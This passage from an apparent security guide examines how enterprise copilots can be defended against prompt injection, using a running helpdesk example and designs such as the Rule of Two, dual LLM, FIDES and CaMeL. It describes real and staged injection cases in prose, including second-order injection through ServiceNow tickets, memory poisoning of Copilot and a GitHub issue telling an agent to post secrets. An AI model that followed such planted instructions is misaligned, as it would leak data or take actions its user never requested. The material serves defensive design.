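A copilot can do damage without sending anything out of the company, because it can also make requests to internal systems. Many of those systems rely on the old assumption that if a request comes from the company network with an employee's valid credentials, the employee must want it.

It was never perfectly safe to assume that an employee wanted whatever their account requested, since a thief with a stolen password can send the same request. But an honest employee normally had to choose an action before it happened. With the helpdesk copilot, an employee, Ann, can ask about the VPN, and a stranger's email in her inbox can lead the copilot to start a password reset. The reset system can authenticate the request (establish whose account it came from) and authorise it (establish that the account may do this), but neither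 check shows whether Ann wanted a reset.

Web developers face a similar problem in cross-site request forgery, where a hostile web page makes a visitor's browser send a request to another site using the visitor's login there. The other site can defend against this by including in its forms a secret value that the hostile page can't read. This doesn't work for a copilot, because the same program sends both the requests Ann wanted and those the email caused, and it could attach the secret to either.

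David C therefore equates the impact of an injection with the worst an attacker could do with direct access to the copilot's tools. The impact depends on what the tools can do and whose permissions they use.

### Excessive agency

OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* describes three ways a model can have too much power. It may have tools it doesn't need, its tools may have permissions they don't need, or it may take high-impact actions without an independent check. OWASP distinguishes this from improper output handling. A team could validate every reset request correctly and still have given the copilot a reset tool it shouldn't have.

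In OWASP's main example, an assistant summarises a person's mail, but the extension it uses can also send mail. A hostile email makes the assistant search the inbox for sensitive information and forward it to the attacker. Either a read-only extension or a read-only login would prevent this.

### Three ways to hold authority

The copilot can use the employee's permissions. When Ann signs in, the copilot receives a token, a digital pass that lets it act on her behalf. Microsoft's *What are agent identities* calls this delegated access and says the user controls which rights to delegate. How much an attacker can do then depends on whose copilot reads the hostile text. A new employee's copilot may be able to do very little, while an administrator's may be able to change thousands of accounts.

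Using one shared service account for everybody makes a copilot simpler to build, but that account needs enough permissions for anything any user might ask. OWASP gives the example of a tool that should read only the current user's files but connects with an account that can read everyone's. An attacker gains the same broad access whichever user they target. A curious employee could also ask the copilot for files they aren't allowed to open.

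The copilot can also have its own identity. Entra, Microsoft's identity system, supports this, and Microsoft recommends it for agents that work without a user, such as those that run scheduled monitoring. If that identity has narrow permissions, an attacker gains little. But if it can reset any password at any time, it is effectively a shared service account.

| How the copilot holds authority | What a successful injection gains | Whom the receiving system's log names |
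|---|---|---|
| The user's delegated permissions | Whatever this user has delegated | The user, and the copilot if the system records both |
| A shared service account | Whatever the account can do, whoever the user is | The service account, and the user only if the copilot's software passes on the name |
| A separate identity with narrow, short-lived permissions | The few actions possible at that moment | The copilot, and the user only if the request includes one |

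Separate agent identities may also share a weak point. In Entra, a "blueprint" holds the credentials for all its agent identities. Compass Security's *Entra Agent ID from a Security Perspective* (2026) warns that compromising those credentials may affect every identity under the blueprint.

Microsoft's *Defend against indirect prompt injection attacks* recommends giving agents privileges only when they need them and removing them after each use. This is very useful against someone who steals a token, but it helps against injection only if the attacker's text can't trigger the grant. If the software grants a five-minute permission to reset a password whenever the model's output requests it, a hostile email can trigger that request. The permission should depend on something outside the model, such as Ann pressing a button marked "Reset my password".

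It is probably best for a copilot that serves signed-in employees to have its own identity and also present the employee's token. The receiving system then permits only actions that both the copilot and the employee are allowed to take, so an administrator's copilot can't use all of the administrator's permissions.

### What the audit log can establish

The combination also produces better records. Red Canary, a security company, staged an example in which an agent emailed an invoice to a finance chief on behalf of a user called Matt. The company says the log entry contained identifiers for both the agent and Matt. If the entry had contained only Matt's identifier, an investigator would have had no reason to ask what the agent had read beforehand.

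In Microsoft 365, a Copilot record lists the user, the time, the files and emails that Copilot accessed, and any agent involved. Microsoft says the record also flags any item in which the company detected a prompt injection. The flag is useful, but its absence is little evidence that an item is safe, because attacks like EchoLeak and ReLeak got past Microsoft's classifier. Splunk's *Getting Started With Copilot Log Analysis for Security in Microsoft 365* adds that the audit log holds only metadata, so investigators have to get the text of prompts and answers from another Microsoft tool.

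They also have to search for Copilot interactions, because when an employee reads a file through Copilot, the log contains one of these instead of the usual file-access event. Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You* describes this as correct, since the employee never opened the file directly. However, an alert that counts only file-access events would miss someone who used Copilot to go through hundreds of documents.

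Pistachio, a security-training company, found a more serious problem in July 2025. If a user asked Copilot to summarise a file and not link to it, the log showed no access to the file. Microsoft fixed this in August 2025 but told Pistachio that it had no plans to tell customers. Some companies probably have gaps in their logs from before the fix and don't know it.

Even with a complete log, an investigator can only list the texts that might have caused a request, not prove that a particular email did. To make that list useful, the helpdesk team should record what the employee typed, every text in the copilot's context, the tool call and its arguments, and both identities. The team should also keep the version of each text that the copilot read, because an attacker who altered a wiki page can change it back afterwards.

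This matters for employees as well as investigators. Ann could be blamed for a request she never made, and a dishonest colleague could blame the copilot for his own request. In *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a draft from the US standards agency NIST, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) ask for suggestions on how to tie an agent's actions to a human authorisation in a way that nobody can later deny, but they don't offer an answer.

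### Dropping to the author's privileges

David C recommends a rule that came out of an online discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista. When a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. A company wouldn't let an outsider use its privileged tools, so a model reading the outsider's email shouldn't have access to them either.

This is the influence rule applied to actions. Permissions don't form a single scale, because a finance clerk can do things that an IT technician can't, and vice versa. The rule is therefore best expressed as an intersection, meaning whatever all the parties have in common:

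**what the copilot may do = the user's permissions ∩ the permissions of everyone whose text is in the context**

Suppose that every employee may reset their own password, administrators may reset anyone's, and outsiders may reset nobody's. Leaving aside the system prompt, which the helpdesk's own team wrote, the rule gives these results:

| Who is using the copilot | Whose text is in the context | Whose password the copilot may reset |
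|---|---|---|
| Ann, an employee | Ann's | Ann's |
| Ann | Ann's and a supplier's | Nobody's |
| Ben, an administrator | Ben's | Anyone's |
| Ben | Ben's and a ticket from Carla, a temporary worker | Carla's |

The last row shows that the rule can preserve a useful function. If Carla's ticket asks for a reset of her own password, Ben's copilot can start it. If the ticket contains an instruction to reset the chief executive's password, the copilot can't, because Carla couldn't have done so herself. But once a wiki page that thousands of employees can edit is in the context, the copilot can't reset any password, because there is no password that all of those employees are allowed to reset.

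Ordinary software has to enforce the rule. When the supplier's email enters Ann's context, the software removes the reset tool so the model cannot call it. The tool has to stay unavailable for the rest of the chat because the email remains in the history.

If Ann asks about the VPN and then wants a reset, the copilot can give her a link to the reset page, or the software can open a new chat that contains only her request. Either way, she loses only perhaps half a minute. The inconvenience is greater if the copilot searches her mailbox before every answer, so it should do that only when a question requires it.

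The rule restricts some jobs much more. A salesperson may want a copilot to read customers' emails and update their records, which means acting on outsiders' text all day. The rule still allows some of this, because outsiders sometimes have privileges of their own. If customers can change their own delivery address on the company's website, the copilot can change it for them after reading an email, provided the company has confirmed who sent it. But it couldn't give them a discount. For many sales teams, this restriction would remove much of the reason for having the copilot.

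Taken literally, the rule would also stop the helpdesk copilot from answering Ann's question. The supplier isn't allowed to read the company wiki, so a copilot with the supplier's email in its context couldn't read it either. David C applies the rule to privileged tools, and it seems reasonable to relax the rule for reading if the answer can reach only Ann, which requires closing the routes by which answers leak data.

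### How a stranger's text becomes an internal record

The privilege-drop rule works only if the software can identify who wrote each text, and copilots can easily obscure this. For example, the helpdesk copilot might read a forged supplier email on Monday and summarise it in a ticket, with the copilot, or perhaps Ann, recorded as the author. On Wednesday, Ben's copilot reads the ticket, which looks like an internal record and may not name the supplier at all.

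Security researchers call this second-order injection. The attacker's text sits in storage and takes effect when somebody else's copilot reads it. A 2025 finding about ServiceNow, a platform that many companies use to run their helpdesks, shows how such an attack can give the attacker higher privileges. AppOmni, which sells security software for such platforms, set up AI agents that only an administrator could use. One categorised tickets, and another could read and change records.

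AppOmni then created a user who could write tickets but couldn't read anyone else's. This user, the attacker, put instructions in a ticket's description. When the administrator had the first agent process the ticket, it called the second, which copied the contents of a confidential ticket into the attacker's ticket, where the attacker could read them. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, the agents gave the attacker an administrator's role or sent records out by email.

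The agents worked with the permissions of the person who started the task, not those of the ticket's author. The privilege-drop rule would have blocked the copying, because the ticket's author had no right to read the confidential record. The second agent's trust in the first was another weakness, because nothing in the internal request showed that it had begun with the text of a ticket.

By default, ServiceNow put agents on the same channel into one team and let them discover each other, which made the attack easier. ServiceNow told AppOmni that this behaviour was intended. According to The Hacker News' *ServiceNow AI Agents Can Be Tricked* (2025), the company then updated its documentation to explain the risks more clearly. AppOmni recommends having a person supervise powerful tools and putting agents in separate teams, so that an agent that reads tickets can't recruit one that changes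 records. Separate teams are the stronger control because they work even when nobody is paying attention.

### Memory

Many assistants also have a memory, a store of notes that the software adds to the context of later chats. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (August 2026) described a way to plant text in the memory of Microsoft's consumer Copilot. When a user asked Copilot to summarise a web page that contained hidden instructions, it returned a normal-looking summary and saved the attacker's text as a memory. That text then entered every later chat until the user found and deleted it.

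Changing the password, ending all sessions and re-enrolling the device didn't help, because those steps remove an attacker's access to an account and the attacker no longer needed access. Varonis also found that the change to the memory left no log entry that security tools would flag. In one demonstration, the saved text made Copilot describe a known software vulnerability as harmless.

Microsoft released fixes on 18 August 2026, about eight months after Varonis reported the flaws, and Varonis knew of no real attacks that used them. Enterprise products have had similar problems. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, which is mostly about Microsoft 365 Copilot, describes a chain of flaws that includes hijacking long-term memory. Microsoft has also seen many real attempts to plant lasting recommendations in assistants' memories through links that pre-fill a prompt. In Microsoft's illustration,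 a finance chief clicks a "Summarize with AI" button on a blog, and weeks later the assistant recommends the supplier named in the button's hidden instruction.

Storing untrusted text in memory is particularly risky because the software loads memory so often. If one entry came from a web page, every chat that includes it falls to the lowest trust level. The helpdesk copilot could avoid this by saving only what the employee types into a separate "remember this" box. It would learn less about each employee, but a helpdesk assistant needs to know little about them.

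Stored text can also spread if copilots copy it into new records. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (Matsuoka, 2026) uses a theoretical model to show that harmful text can keep spreading between two groups of agents even when it would die out within either group alone. As a simpler example with invented numbers, suppose each poisoned ticket leads copilots to write an average of 0.6 more poisoned tickets and 0.5 poisoned wiki pages, and each poisoned page leads to 0.5 tickets and 0.6 pages. The poisoned text would die out if it spread only among tickets or only among pages, but with both, each poisoned record leads to an average of 1.1 new ones, so the total keeps growing.

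Poisoned tickets alone would die out, as would poisoned pages alone, because 0.6 is less than one. When both spread, each poisoned item produces 1.1 new ones, so the number grows by about 10% per round. The growth would stop if the copilot couldn't edit the wiki. Matsuoka found no public record, up to 5 August 2026, of an attack that completed his whole scenario, from a dormant instruction to large-scale destruction, but each step has worked in experiments.

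### Keeping the origin attached

The first remedy is to record where stored text came from. When the helpdesk copilot writes a ticket, its software should save the copilot's identity, the employee it was working for, the sources in the context and the lowest trust level among them. A ticket based partly on a supplier's email therefore gets level 0, the lowest.

The software has to write this label in a separate field that the model can't change. If the model wrote the label as part of the ticket, a hostile email could make it write a false one.

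Text also has to keep its level when it is rewritten. If Ben's copilot summarises the ticket for a weekly report, the report is still at level 0, and so is a wiki page based on the report. Each rewrite makes the text look more like the company's own and removes clues to its source, but an attacker's instruction or false claim can remain through all of them. A summary should gain a higher level only when someone with the authority to write that page checks the content against an independent source and takes responsibility for it.

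If an older system has no field for a trust level, the team can store the copilot's records separately, or give the copilot an account whose records every other agent treats as level 0. This is crude because it also lowers the trust level of text that the copilot based only on trusted sources, but it is much safer than letting the copilot write under Ann's name.

### Making the receiving system check

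The receiving system also has to decide whether to accept a request. OWASP recommends complete mediation, which means checking every request against the security policy instead of relying on the model to decide what is allowed. Android Developers' *Mitigate excessive agency vulnerabilities* likewise advises backend services to authenticate, authorise and validate each request themselves.

An attack on Instagram in 2026 shows what can happen without such a check. Krebs on Security (2026) reported that attackers asked Meta's AI support assistant to link a new email address to someone else's account. The assistant sent a code to that address, and the attackers used the code to reset the account's password. The Decoder reported that the campaign lasted nearly seven weeks. Meta said up to 20,225 accounts were affected, though the real owners may have requested some of the resets.

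SecurityWeek's *Meta Says 20000 Instagram Accounts Hacked via AI Tool Abuse* reports that, according to Meta, the AI tool worked as intended. The fault was in separate code, which failed to check that the email address belonged to the account. Although Instagram is a consumer service and the attackers typed their requests directly rather than using indirect injection, the helpdesk's reset system needs the same check. Comparing two email addresses would have stopped all of the requests, whereas a better-behaved model might have refused only some of them.

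As with the asset database, the helpdesk's reset system should take the employee's identity from the login, in this case the token, and never from the model. It should check that both the employee and the copilot are allowed to reset the account, and reject the request if its trust level is too low. The copilot's software has to attach that level because the reset system has no access to the context. The reset system should send the reset link only to a contact address already on file.

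That last step limits the harm even if a hostile email does cause a reset, but the helpdesk copilot can also read staff mail. If the reset link arrives in Ann's inbox, injected text might make the copilot find the link and leak it. The system should therefore send the link to her phone, or the team should exclude reset messages from the copilot's search. Checking the mail tool and the reset tool separately would probably miss this risk, because each looks safe on its own.

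### Does this make everything untrusted?

A manager could object that these rules would label most of the company's information as untrusted. Customers write many of the tickets, suppliers write much of the mail, and copilots write more of the summaries every month. After a year or two, nearly everything might be at level 0, which would make a copilot that can't use level-0 text useless.

The labels probably would spread that far in many companies, but a copilot can still use labelled text if the team separates reading from acting. Companies already handle email this way. Employees read outsiders' messages all day, but a sensible accounts department doesn't act on an emailed request to change a supplier's bank details until it has checked with the supplier through a contact it already has.

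With level-0 text in its context, the helpdesk copilot could still search the wiki, explain the VPN steps, summarise a ticket and draft a reply for Ann. It could also open a new ticket, because a stranger can already do that by writing to the helpdesk. It couldn't reset a password, change who owns a laptop, edit the wiki or save a memory. Most helpdesk questions need only the permitted functions, so most employees would rarely notice the restriction.

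Reading still carries some risk, because an answer can leak data or contain an attacker's false statement that Ann then acts on herself.

The separation works least well where the content of an outsider's message has to determine the action, as with invoices, refunds and sales orders. Software that tracks labels can permit some of these actions more precisely. Without it, the team has to limit the copilot to a few of these actions whose worst outcome is acceptable, such as refunds below $20 to the card the customer originally used.

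## Which designs limit what untrusted output can do?

The helpdesk team can remove the reset tool whenever an outsider's text enters the chat. Several published designs develop the same idea. They assume that an attacker will sometimes fool the model and arrange the rest of the system so that a fooled model can't do much harm. They range from rules that a team can apply in one meeting to designs that need a custom-built interpreter, and most make the copilot less useful.

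### Counting dangerous abilities

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) names three abilities that together let an attacker steal data through an agent: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content that can carry the attacker's instructions, and a way to communicate externally that can send the data out. Removing any one of them prevents the theft.

A single tool can have all three abilities. Willison's example is GitHub's MCP server, which could read public issues, open private repositories and propose code changes that outsiders could see. An employee can also accidentally combine all three by connecting a mail tool from one supplier to a web tool from another. The suppliers can't fix this problem because it doesn't come from a mistake in either tool.

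The helpdesk copilot has all three abilities until the team stops its answers from loading images and linking to addresses that the model wrote. Even then, a stranger's email could cause a password reset, because a reset doesn't send data out. The trifecta describes data theft, so it doesn't cover this kind of harm.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) does cover it. Under this rule, an agent may have no more than two of these properties in one session:

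- **A:** it processes untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change something or communicate externally.

If a task needs all three, Meta says the agent shouldn't work without supervision, such as human approval. A new session starts with an empty context, so a team can often split the work. The helpdesk copilot might have three modes:

| Task | A | B | C | How the team enforces the limit |
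|---|---|---|---|---|
| Explain a VPN fault using Ann's mail and the wiki | Yes | Yes | No | Turn off every tool that changes something, and keep outside images and links out of the answer |
| Reset Ann's password | No | Yes | Yes | Open a new chat that contains only what Ann typed |
| Find a printer driver on the public web | Yes | No | Yes | Use a separate chat with no access to mail, the wiki or the asset database |

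The web search counts as external communication because the search terms leave the company. Meta also allows an agent to change modes during a session. For example, the agent could browse the web first, then permanently lose its ability to communicate externally before it gets access to internal systems. The change has to be permanent because the web text stays in the agent's context.

The rule is easy to apply but coarse. Property B doesn't distinguish between access to one employee's laptop model and access to the whole payroll. An agent with only properties A and C could still fill the ticket queue with junk, unless the team counts the queue as a sensitive system. Meta presents the rule as an addition to least privilege (giving each component only the permissions it needs), and notes that the rule doesn't prevent an agent's own mistakes or false statements in its answers.

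### A reader without tools

Many useful tasks need all three abilities. Other designs therefore keep the abilities but divide them between separate parts of the system.

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed using two models. The privileged model takes the user's instructions and can call tools, but never reads untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. Ordinary software, called the controller, passes information between them. If Ann asks for a summary of her latest email, the system works like this:

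1. The privileged model asks for the email.
2. The controller fetches it, stores it as VAR1, and gives the privileged model only that name.
3. The privileged model asks for a summary of VAR1.
4. The controller gives the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as VAR2.
5. The privileged model asks the controller to show VAR2 to Ann.

A hostile email can corrupt the summary, but the quarantined model that reads the email can't call tools, and the privileged model that can call tools never receives the email or the summary. In Willison's design, the privileged model may receive the quarantined model's answer only if ordinary code can confirm that it comes from a fixed list, such as "hardware", "network" or "account".

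Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and one programming mistake that shows untrusted text to the privileged model removes the protection. The summary could also persuade Ann to copy private data into an attacker's website herself.

Researchers at Google DeepMind later pointed out another weakness. The dual-LLM pattern protects the control flow (which steps happen and in what order) but not the data flow (which values go into those steps). Suppose Ann asks the copilot to send her laptop's warranty document to a repair firm whose address is in an email. The privileged model correctly decides to send the document, but the email can make the quarantined model return an attacker's address.

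### Six design patterns

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) lists the dual-LLM pattern as one of six design patterns. All six follow the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must be unable to trigger a consequential action. The patterns differ in how much influence hostile text still has.

| Pattern | How it works | What hostile data can still change | A suitable helpdesk task |
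|---|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | The model chooses from a fixed set of actions and never sees the results | Nothing the model does | Reset my password |
| Plan-then-execute | The model lists its tool calls before it reads any data | The values in those calls | Send today's schedule to my manager |
| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools reads each item and gives a restricted answer, and the system combines the answers | The answer about that one item | Sort 500 tickets by category |
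| Dual LLM | One model plans and another reads | The stored values | Summarise an email thread |
| Code-then-execute | The model writes a program that can call tools and quarantined models | The values the program handles | Gather details from several emails into a report |
| Context-minimisation | The software removes text from the context once the model has used it | Any step taken before the removal | Turn a question into a database query, then write the answer without the question in the context |

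The last pattern mainly protects against hostile text in the user's request, such as something Ann pastes in from a website. The other five mostly assume that her request is safe.

The case studies also show how a pattern can fail. One assistant organises files using only two commands, fixed in advance, one to find files and one to move them. A hostile file could still make the assistant find confidential documents and move them to a public network drive, because each command could do too much.

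Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think a fixed plan would make an email and calendar assistant only slightly less useful, because the choice of actions should rarely depend on what an email says. A coding assistant would become much less useful under the safest design they consider. In that design, a quarantined model converts outside documentation into a strict description of the available functions, with names of no more than, say, 30 characters. The conversion would probably remove an injection, but it would also remove the explanations and examples that programmers often read documentation for.

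Beurer-Kellner and colleagues conclude that general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees with current models, but that agents built for one application can. This conclusion is more useful to a helpdesk, where the team can list most of the jobs in advance, than to a company that bought one assistant to do everything.

### Labels and checks in FIDES

FIDES, built by Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, enforces the influence rule in software. In May 2026, Microsoft added it as an experimental feature to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) explains how this version works.

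Each piece of content has an integrity label, which is trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label, which is public, private or user identity. User identity is the most sensitive level and covers personal information. The developer sets these labels where the data enters, for example by writing the mail tool to mark every email as untrusted.

When the agent reads several items, FIDES combines their labels and keeps the more restrictive value of each kind. Untrusted wins over trusted, and the highest confidentiality wins:

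**(trusted, private) combined with (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, private)**

Each tool also has a rule about which context labels it accepts. Before every tool call, ordinary code checks the context's labels against that rule and blocks the call if they don't match. The model selects which calls to attempt, but it can't change the labels or the rule.

Microsoft's example is an agent that sorts public issues on GitHub. An attacker submits what looks like a normal bug report but includes an instruction for the agent to read a file of secrets and post its contents as a comment.

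1. The agent reads the issue. FIDES labels all of it untrusted and public, including the hidden instruction.
2. The model follows the instruction and opens the file. FIDES permits this, and labels the file's contents trusted and private.
3. The context now contains both texts, so its combined label is untrusted and private.
4. The model tries to post the secrets. The comment tool accepts only public contexts, so FIDES blocks the call.

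If the instruction had been to overwrite a file, FIDES would have blocked that too, because the file-writing tool doesn't accept untrusted contexts. In Microsoft's configuration, a person can override either block.

The attack fails even though the model followed the attacker's instructions and nothing detected the injection. But the secrets entered the context, so they stay safe only if every tool that could send them out has a correct rule. The comment tool's confidentiality limit would also allow a comment containing only public text, such as a link to an attacker's fake fix. The team could block the tool in untrusted contexts, but then the agent couldn't comment on any issue it had read.

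### Hiding text so that tools stay available

Once an agent has read one untrusted item, its context stays untrusted for the rest of the run unless the developer removes the item. FIDES reduces this problem with a version of the dual-LLM pattern. It stores untrusted text under a variable name, so the main model receives only the name and its context remains trusted. A quarantined model reads the text when needed. Microsoft's version does this by default, but it requires a second model call and the agent has to work from summaries. *APPA* (2026) describes a related design that creates an isolated branch only when an ordinary agent needs one.

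Hiding text from the main model makes some decisions harder. Suppose Ann asks the copilot to check three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. The main model can't decide whether to create the event without some information about the emails.

Costa and colleagues handle this by restricting the form of the quarantined model's answer. This model first returns only yes or no to indicate whether there is a meeting request. If the answer is yes, it extracts the date, time and participants into a hidden variable, which the main model passes to the calendar tool.

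A rule might let the main model see a yes-or-no answer but not free text. A yes or no carries only one bit of information, which is too little to hold a new instruction from an attacker. If the answer decides whether to schedule a meeting, the attacker can still cause an unwanted meeting but can't trigger a password reset.

### How CaMeL fixes the plan in advance

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind researchers published in 2025, also deals with the substituted address. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains that a privileged model first turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python. For Ann's warranty request, the program might be:

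```python
email = get_latest_email(sender="repair firm")
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find the reply address", email)
document = get_warranty(owner="Ann")
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

The privileged model writes all four lines from Ann's request alone, before any model reads the email. So the email can't add a fifth line, but it can still affect the value of `address`.

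A custom interpreter then runs the program and keeps tags on every value. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), these tags record where a value came from and who may read it. Because `address` came from `email`, the interpreter treats it as untrusted too. Before running the last line, the interpreter checks the rule for sending mail, which might require a recipient the company already knows. If the email supplied an attacker's address, the interpreter blocks the message or asks Ann to approve it.

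FIDES and CaMeL both track labels, but they plan differently. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, explain that CaMeL's plan can't depend on what its tools return, whereas FIDES can reveal hidden text to its planner, which then works under tighter restrictions. CaMeL's program can include conditions, but the model has to write every branch in advance. That works for sending a document, but not well for diagnosing a fault, where the choice of each test depends on earlier results.

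### Security against completed tasks

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES in 2025 on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks and 36 attacker goals in simulated office, travel, banking and workplace-chat environments. They used two OpenAI models, GPT-4o and o1, which are now well behind the best. The completion rates in the table below were measured without attacks and averaged over the four environments. The attack counts leave out cases that the researchers thought AgentDojo had scored incorrectly.

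| Agent | Label checks | Successful attacks, GPT-4o | Tasks completed, GPT-4o | Tasks completed, o1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | Off | 152 | 84% | 84% |
| Ordinary agent | On | 0 | 42% | 44% |
| FIDES | Off | 21 | 61% | 78% |
| FIDES | On | 0 | 50% | 61% |

Costa and colleagues report that, with checks on for both, FIDES with o1 completed 16% more tasks than the ordinary agent. FIDES's completion rate was 23 percentage points lower than that of an unprotected agent. The second comparison is the relevant one for a team deciding whether to add protection to a working copilot.

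AgentDojo uses a fixed set of attacks, so a determined attacker would probably have succeeded more than 21 times against FIDES with its checks off. The zeros recorded with the checks on are stronger evidence, because the checks don't depend on how an attack is worded, though they do depend on correct labels and rules.

Switching from GPT-4o to o1 raised FIDES's completion rate from 41% to 68% on travel tasks, but only from 52.5% to 56.2% on banking tasks. Many of the travel failures seem to have come from GPT-4o's poor handling of hidden variables, which a better model can correct. But many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the rules are meant to prevent. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) suggests that CaMeL will lose less usefulness as models get better at planning. That seems right for tasks the rules permit, but a better model still can't complete tasks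 they forbid.

More recent results for CaMeL support the same conclusion. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, ran it with newer models on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each. They also tested their own agent, Randori, whose checks are always on.

| System | Model | Tasks completed without attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, checks off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 (67%) | 1 of 240 |
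| CaMeL, checks off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 (71%) | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, checks on | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 (38%) | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, checks on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 (38%) | 0 of 357 |
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 (75%) | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 (65%) | 0 of 432 |

These figures come from the developers of a competing system, and 16 tasks are too few for precise estimates. The margin of error on CaMeL's 38% is about 27 percentage points either way. Banking is also an unusually hard test. Costa and colleagues count 44% of banking tasks as requiring actions that depend on what the agent reads, compared with only 5% of office tasks, so an office copilot might lose much less.

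CaMeL blocked nearly every attack even with its checks off. In about two-thirds of the task-attack pairs, the attacker needed a tool call that a program written for that task would never include. Much of the protection on this benchmark therefore came from setting the plan early, which is simpler than tracking every value.

A fixed plan can still let an attacker control the actions if outside text determines which branch of the plan runs. When the task was to read a file and follow its instructions, CaMeL's model once wrote a program with a branch for every tool, so the file's contents determined which tool ran. A team that uses fixed plans should reject any program in which outside text can select a sensitive tool.

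Randori completes more tasks than CaMeL with checks on, partly because its model can specify, before it reads any outside data, which untrusted values the program should accept. Without that ability, Randori still completed 26 of 48 tasks with MiMo-v2.5, so other differences between the two systems matter too. Both successful attacks on Randori used the same task, which was to make a payment described in a text file. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Because the user had asked for the payment described in the file, a label could show only that the instruction was untrusted, not that the payment was wrong.

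On easier tasks, separation can have very little effect on a copilot's usefulness. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tested a simple split between a planner and a reader on Llama-3.1-8B, a small open model. None of 210 attacks succeeded, and nine of ten summaries of harmless web pages still included the main facts. The plan didn't depend on the page's contents, which is the best case for this kind of design.

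Completion rates don't measure speed or human effort. *ToolFence* (2026) found CaMeL significantly slower in its tests than defences based on prompts or filters, partly because the model has to write a whole program. Someone also has to write the security rules and update them when the tools change.

Kolluri and colleagues argue that completion rates also leave out a benefit of tracking labels, which is that users have to approve fewer actions. Many products ask the user to approve every consequential action, whereas an agent that tracks labels needs to ask only when an action would break a rule. The researchers' agent, Prudentia, builds on FIDES and tells the planner about the labels and rules so that the planner can avoid unnecessary violations. On AgentDojo, Prudentia completed up to 9% more tasks than FIDES without any human approval, and reduced the number of approvals by a factor of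 up to 1.9.

### What the labels miss

The most likely failure is a missing label. In Microsoft's version of FIDES, a tool without a label counts as trusted and public. If the helpdesk team adds a mailbox tool and forgets the label, every stranger's email counts as trusted, and the checks will allow any action it triggers. Microsoft is considering a stricter default. For now, a team can write a test that stops the copilot from starting if any tool has no label.

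A correct label doesn't make an answer true. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that instructs the quarantined model to produce an empty summary. The agent then breaks no rule when it sends the useless summary to the right person with the right tool. A stricter rule could ban summaries of untrusted text, but that would remove one of the main uses of an office copilot. The chat panel can instead show Ann that a summary comes from outside text, although she still won't know whether to believe it.

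Some private information can also leak through the agent's choice of actions. Suppose the copilot opens a public ticket only when an employee's private file contains a complaint. The ticket may contain nothing confidential, but anyone who knows this behaviour can infer the complaint. FIDES doesn't track such inferences. Costa and colleagues considered a stronger guarantee impractical because it would in effect ban publicly visible actions after the agent had read anything secret.

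CaMeL does try to track them, but Garby and colleagues found two gaps. The first occurs when a secret, such as whether an account balance exceeds some amount, determines whether a program changes a variable. CaMeL marks the variable as secret only if the program changes it. An unchanged variable also reveals the secret, but it remains marked as public, so the program can send it out.

The second gap is that CaMeL doesn't track what happens in the software that reruns a failed program. Each attempt can reveal one yes-or-no fact about a secret, depending on whether the rules blocked it, so about 20 attempts could reveal a six-digit login code. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) describes a similar problem in a relaxed version of FIDES that lets the planner ask yes-or-no questions about a screen. Repeated questions could eventually reveal everything on it, so the researchers limited the number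 of calls.

Exploiting these gaps would be harder than carrying out an ordinary injection. An attacker would need to influence the program itself, which CaMeL's privileged model writes without reading outside text. The easiest way to do that might be through a user who pastes a stranger's text into the request. For most helpdesks, a forgotten label is probably a more urgent problem.

Garby and colleagues' remedy is the LLMbda calculus, a small programming language for agents in which every value has a label and retries happen inside the tracked part of the system. They used the proof checker Lean to prove that secret inputs can't affect a program's public results, except by changing whether the program finishes. A program can declare an untrusted value trustworthy, but only through an explicit instruction that a reviewer can find. The proof covers the language and its interpreter, so it doesn't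 guarantee that a team has labelled its mailbox correctly.

### Matching the design to the task

A company that buys a finished copilot usually can't rebuild it around FIDES or CaMeL. It can still apply the Rule of Two by choosing which data sources and tools to switch on, and perhaps by giving different groups of staff different combinations. The other designs are for teams that build their own copilots.

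A simple design is often enough for the helpdesk copilot. A password reset needs only a fixed menu of actions and the employee's identity from the login. A model without tools can summarise mail and tickets. To sort tickets, a separate model can read each one and return only a category, so a hostile ticket can at worst end up in the wrong queue.

CaMeL is better when a task has several predictable steps and carries outside data between them, as in Ann's warranty request. FIDES is better when the copilot has to make a small decision along the way, such as whether an email requests a meeting. It is also easier to add to an existing agent, since a developer labels the data sources and tools without redesigning the whole program. Microsoft considers FIDES unnecessary if every input comes from one trusted source and every output goes to one trusted destination, or if the agent has no privileged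 tools and can at worst give a wrong answer.

None of these designs works well for tasks in which an outsider's message has to determine the action, such as dealing with unanswered emails or paying an invoice. The team can separate out the safe parts, for example by letting the copilot draft replies but not send them, or extract an invoice's amount but take the bank details from the company's own records. For the rest, someone has to decide whether to carry out each outsider's request, because a label isn't enough to determine that.

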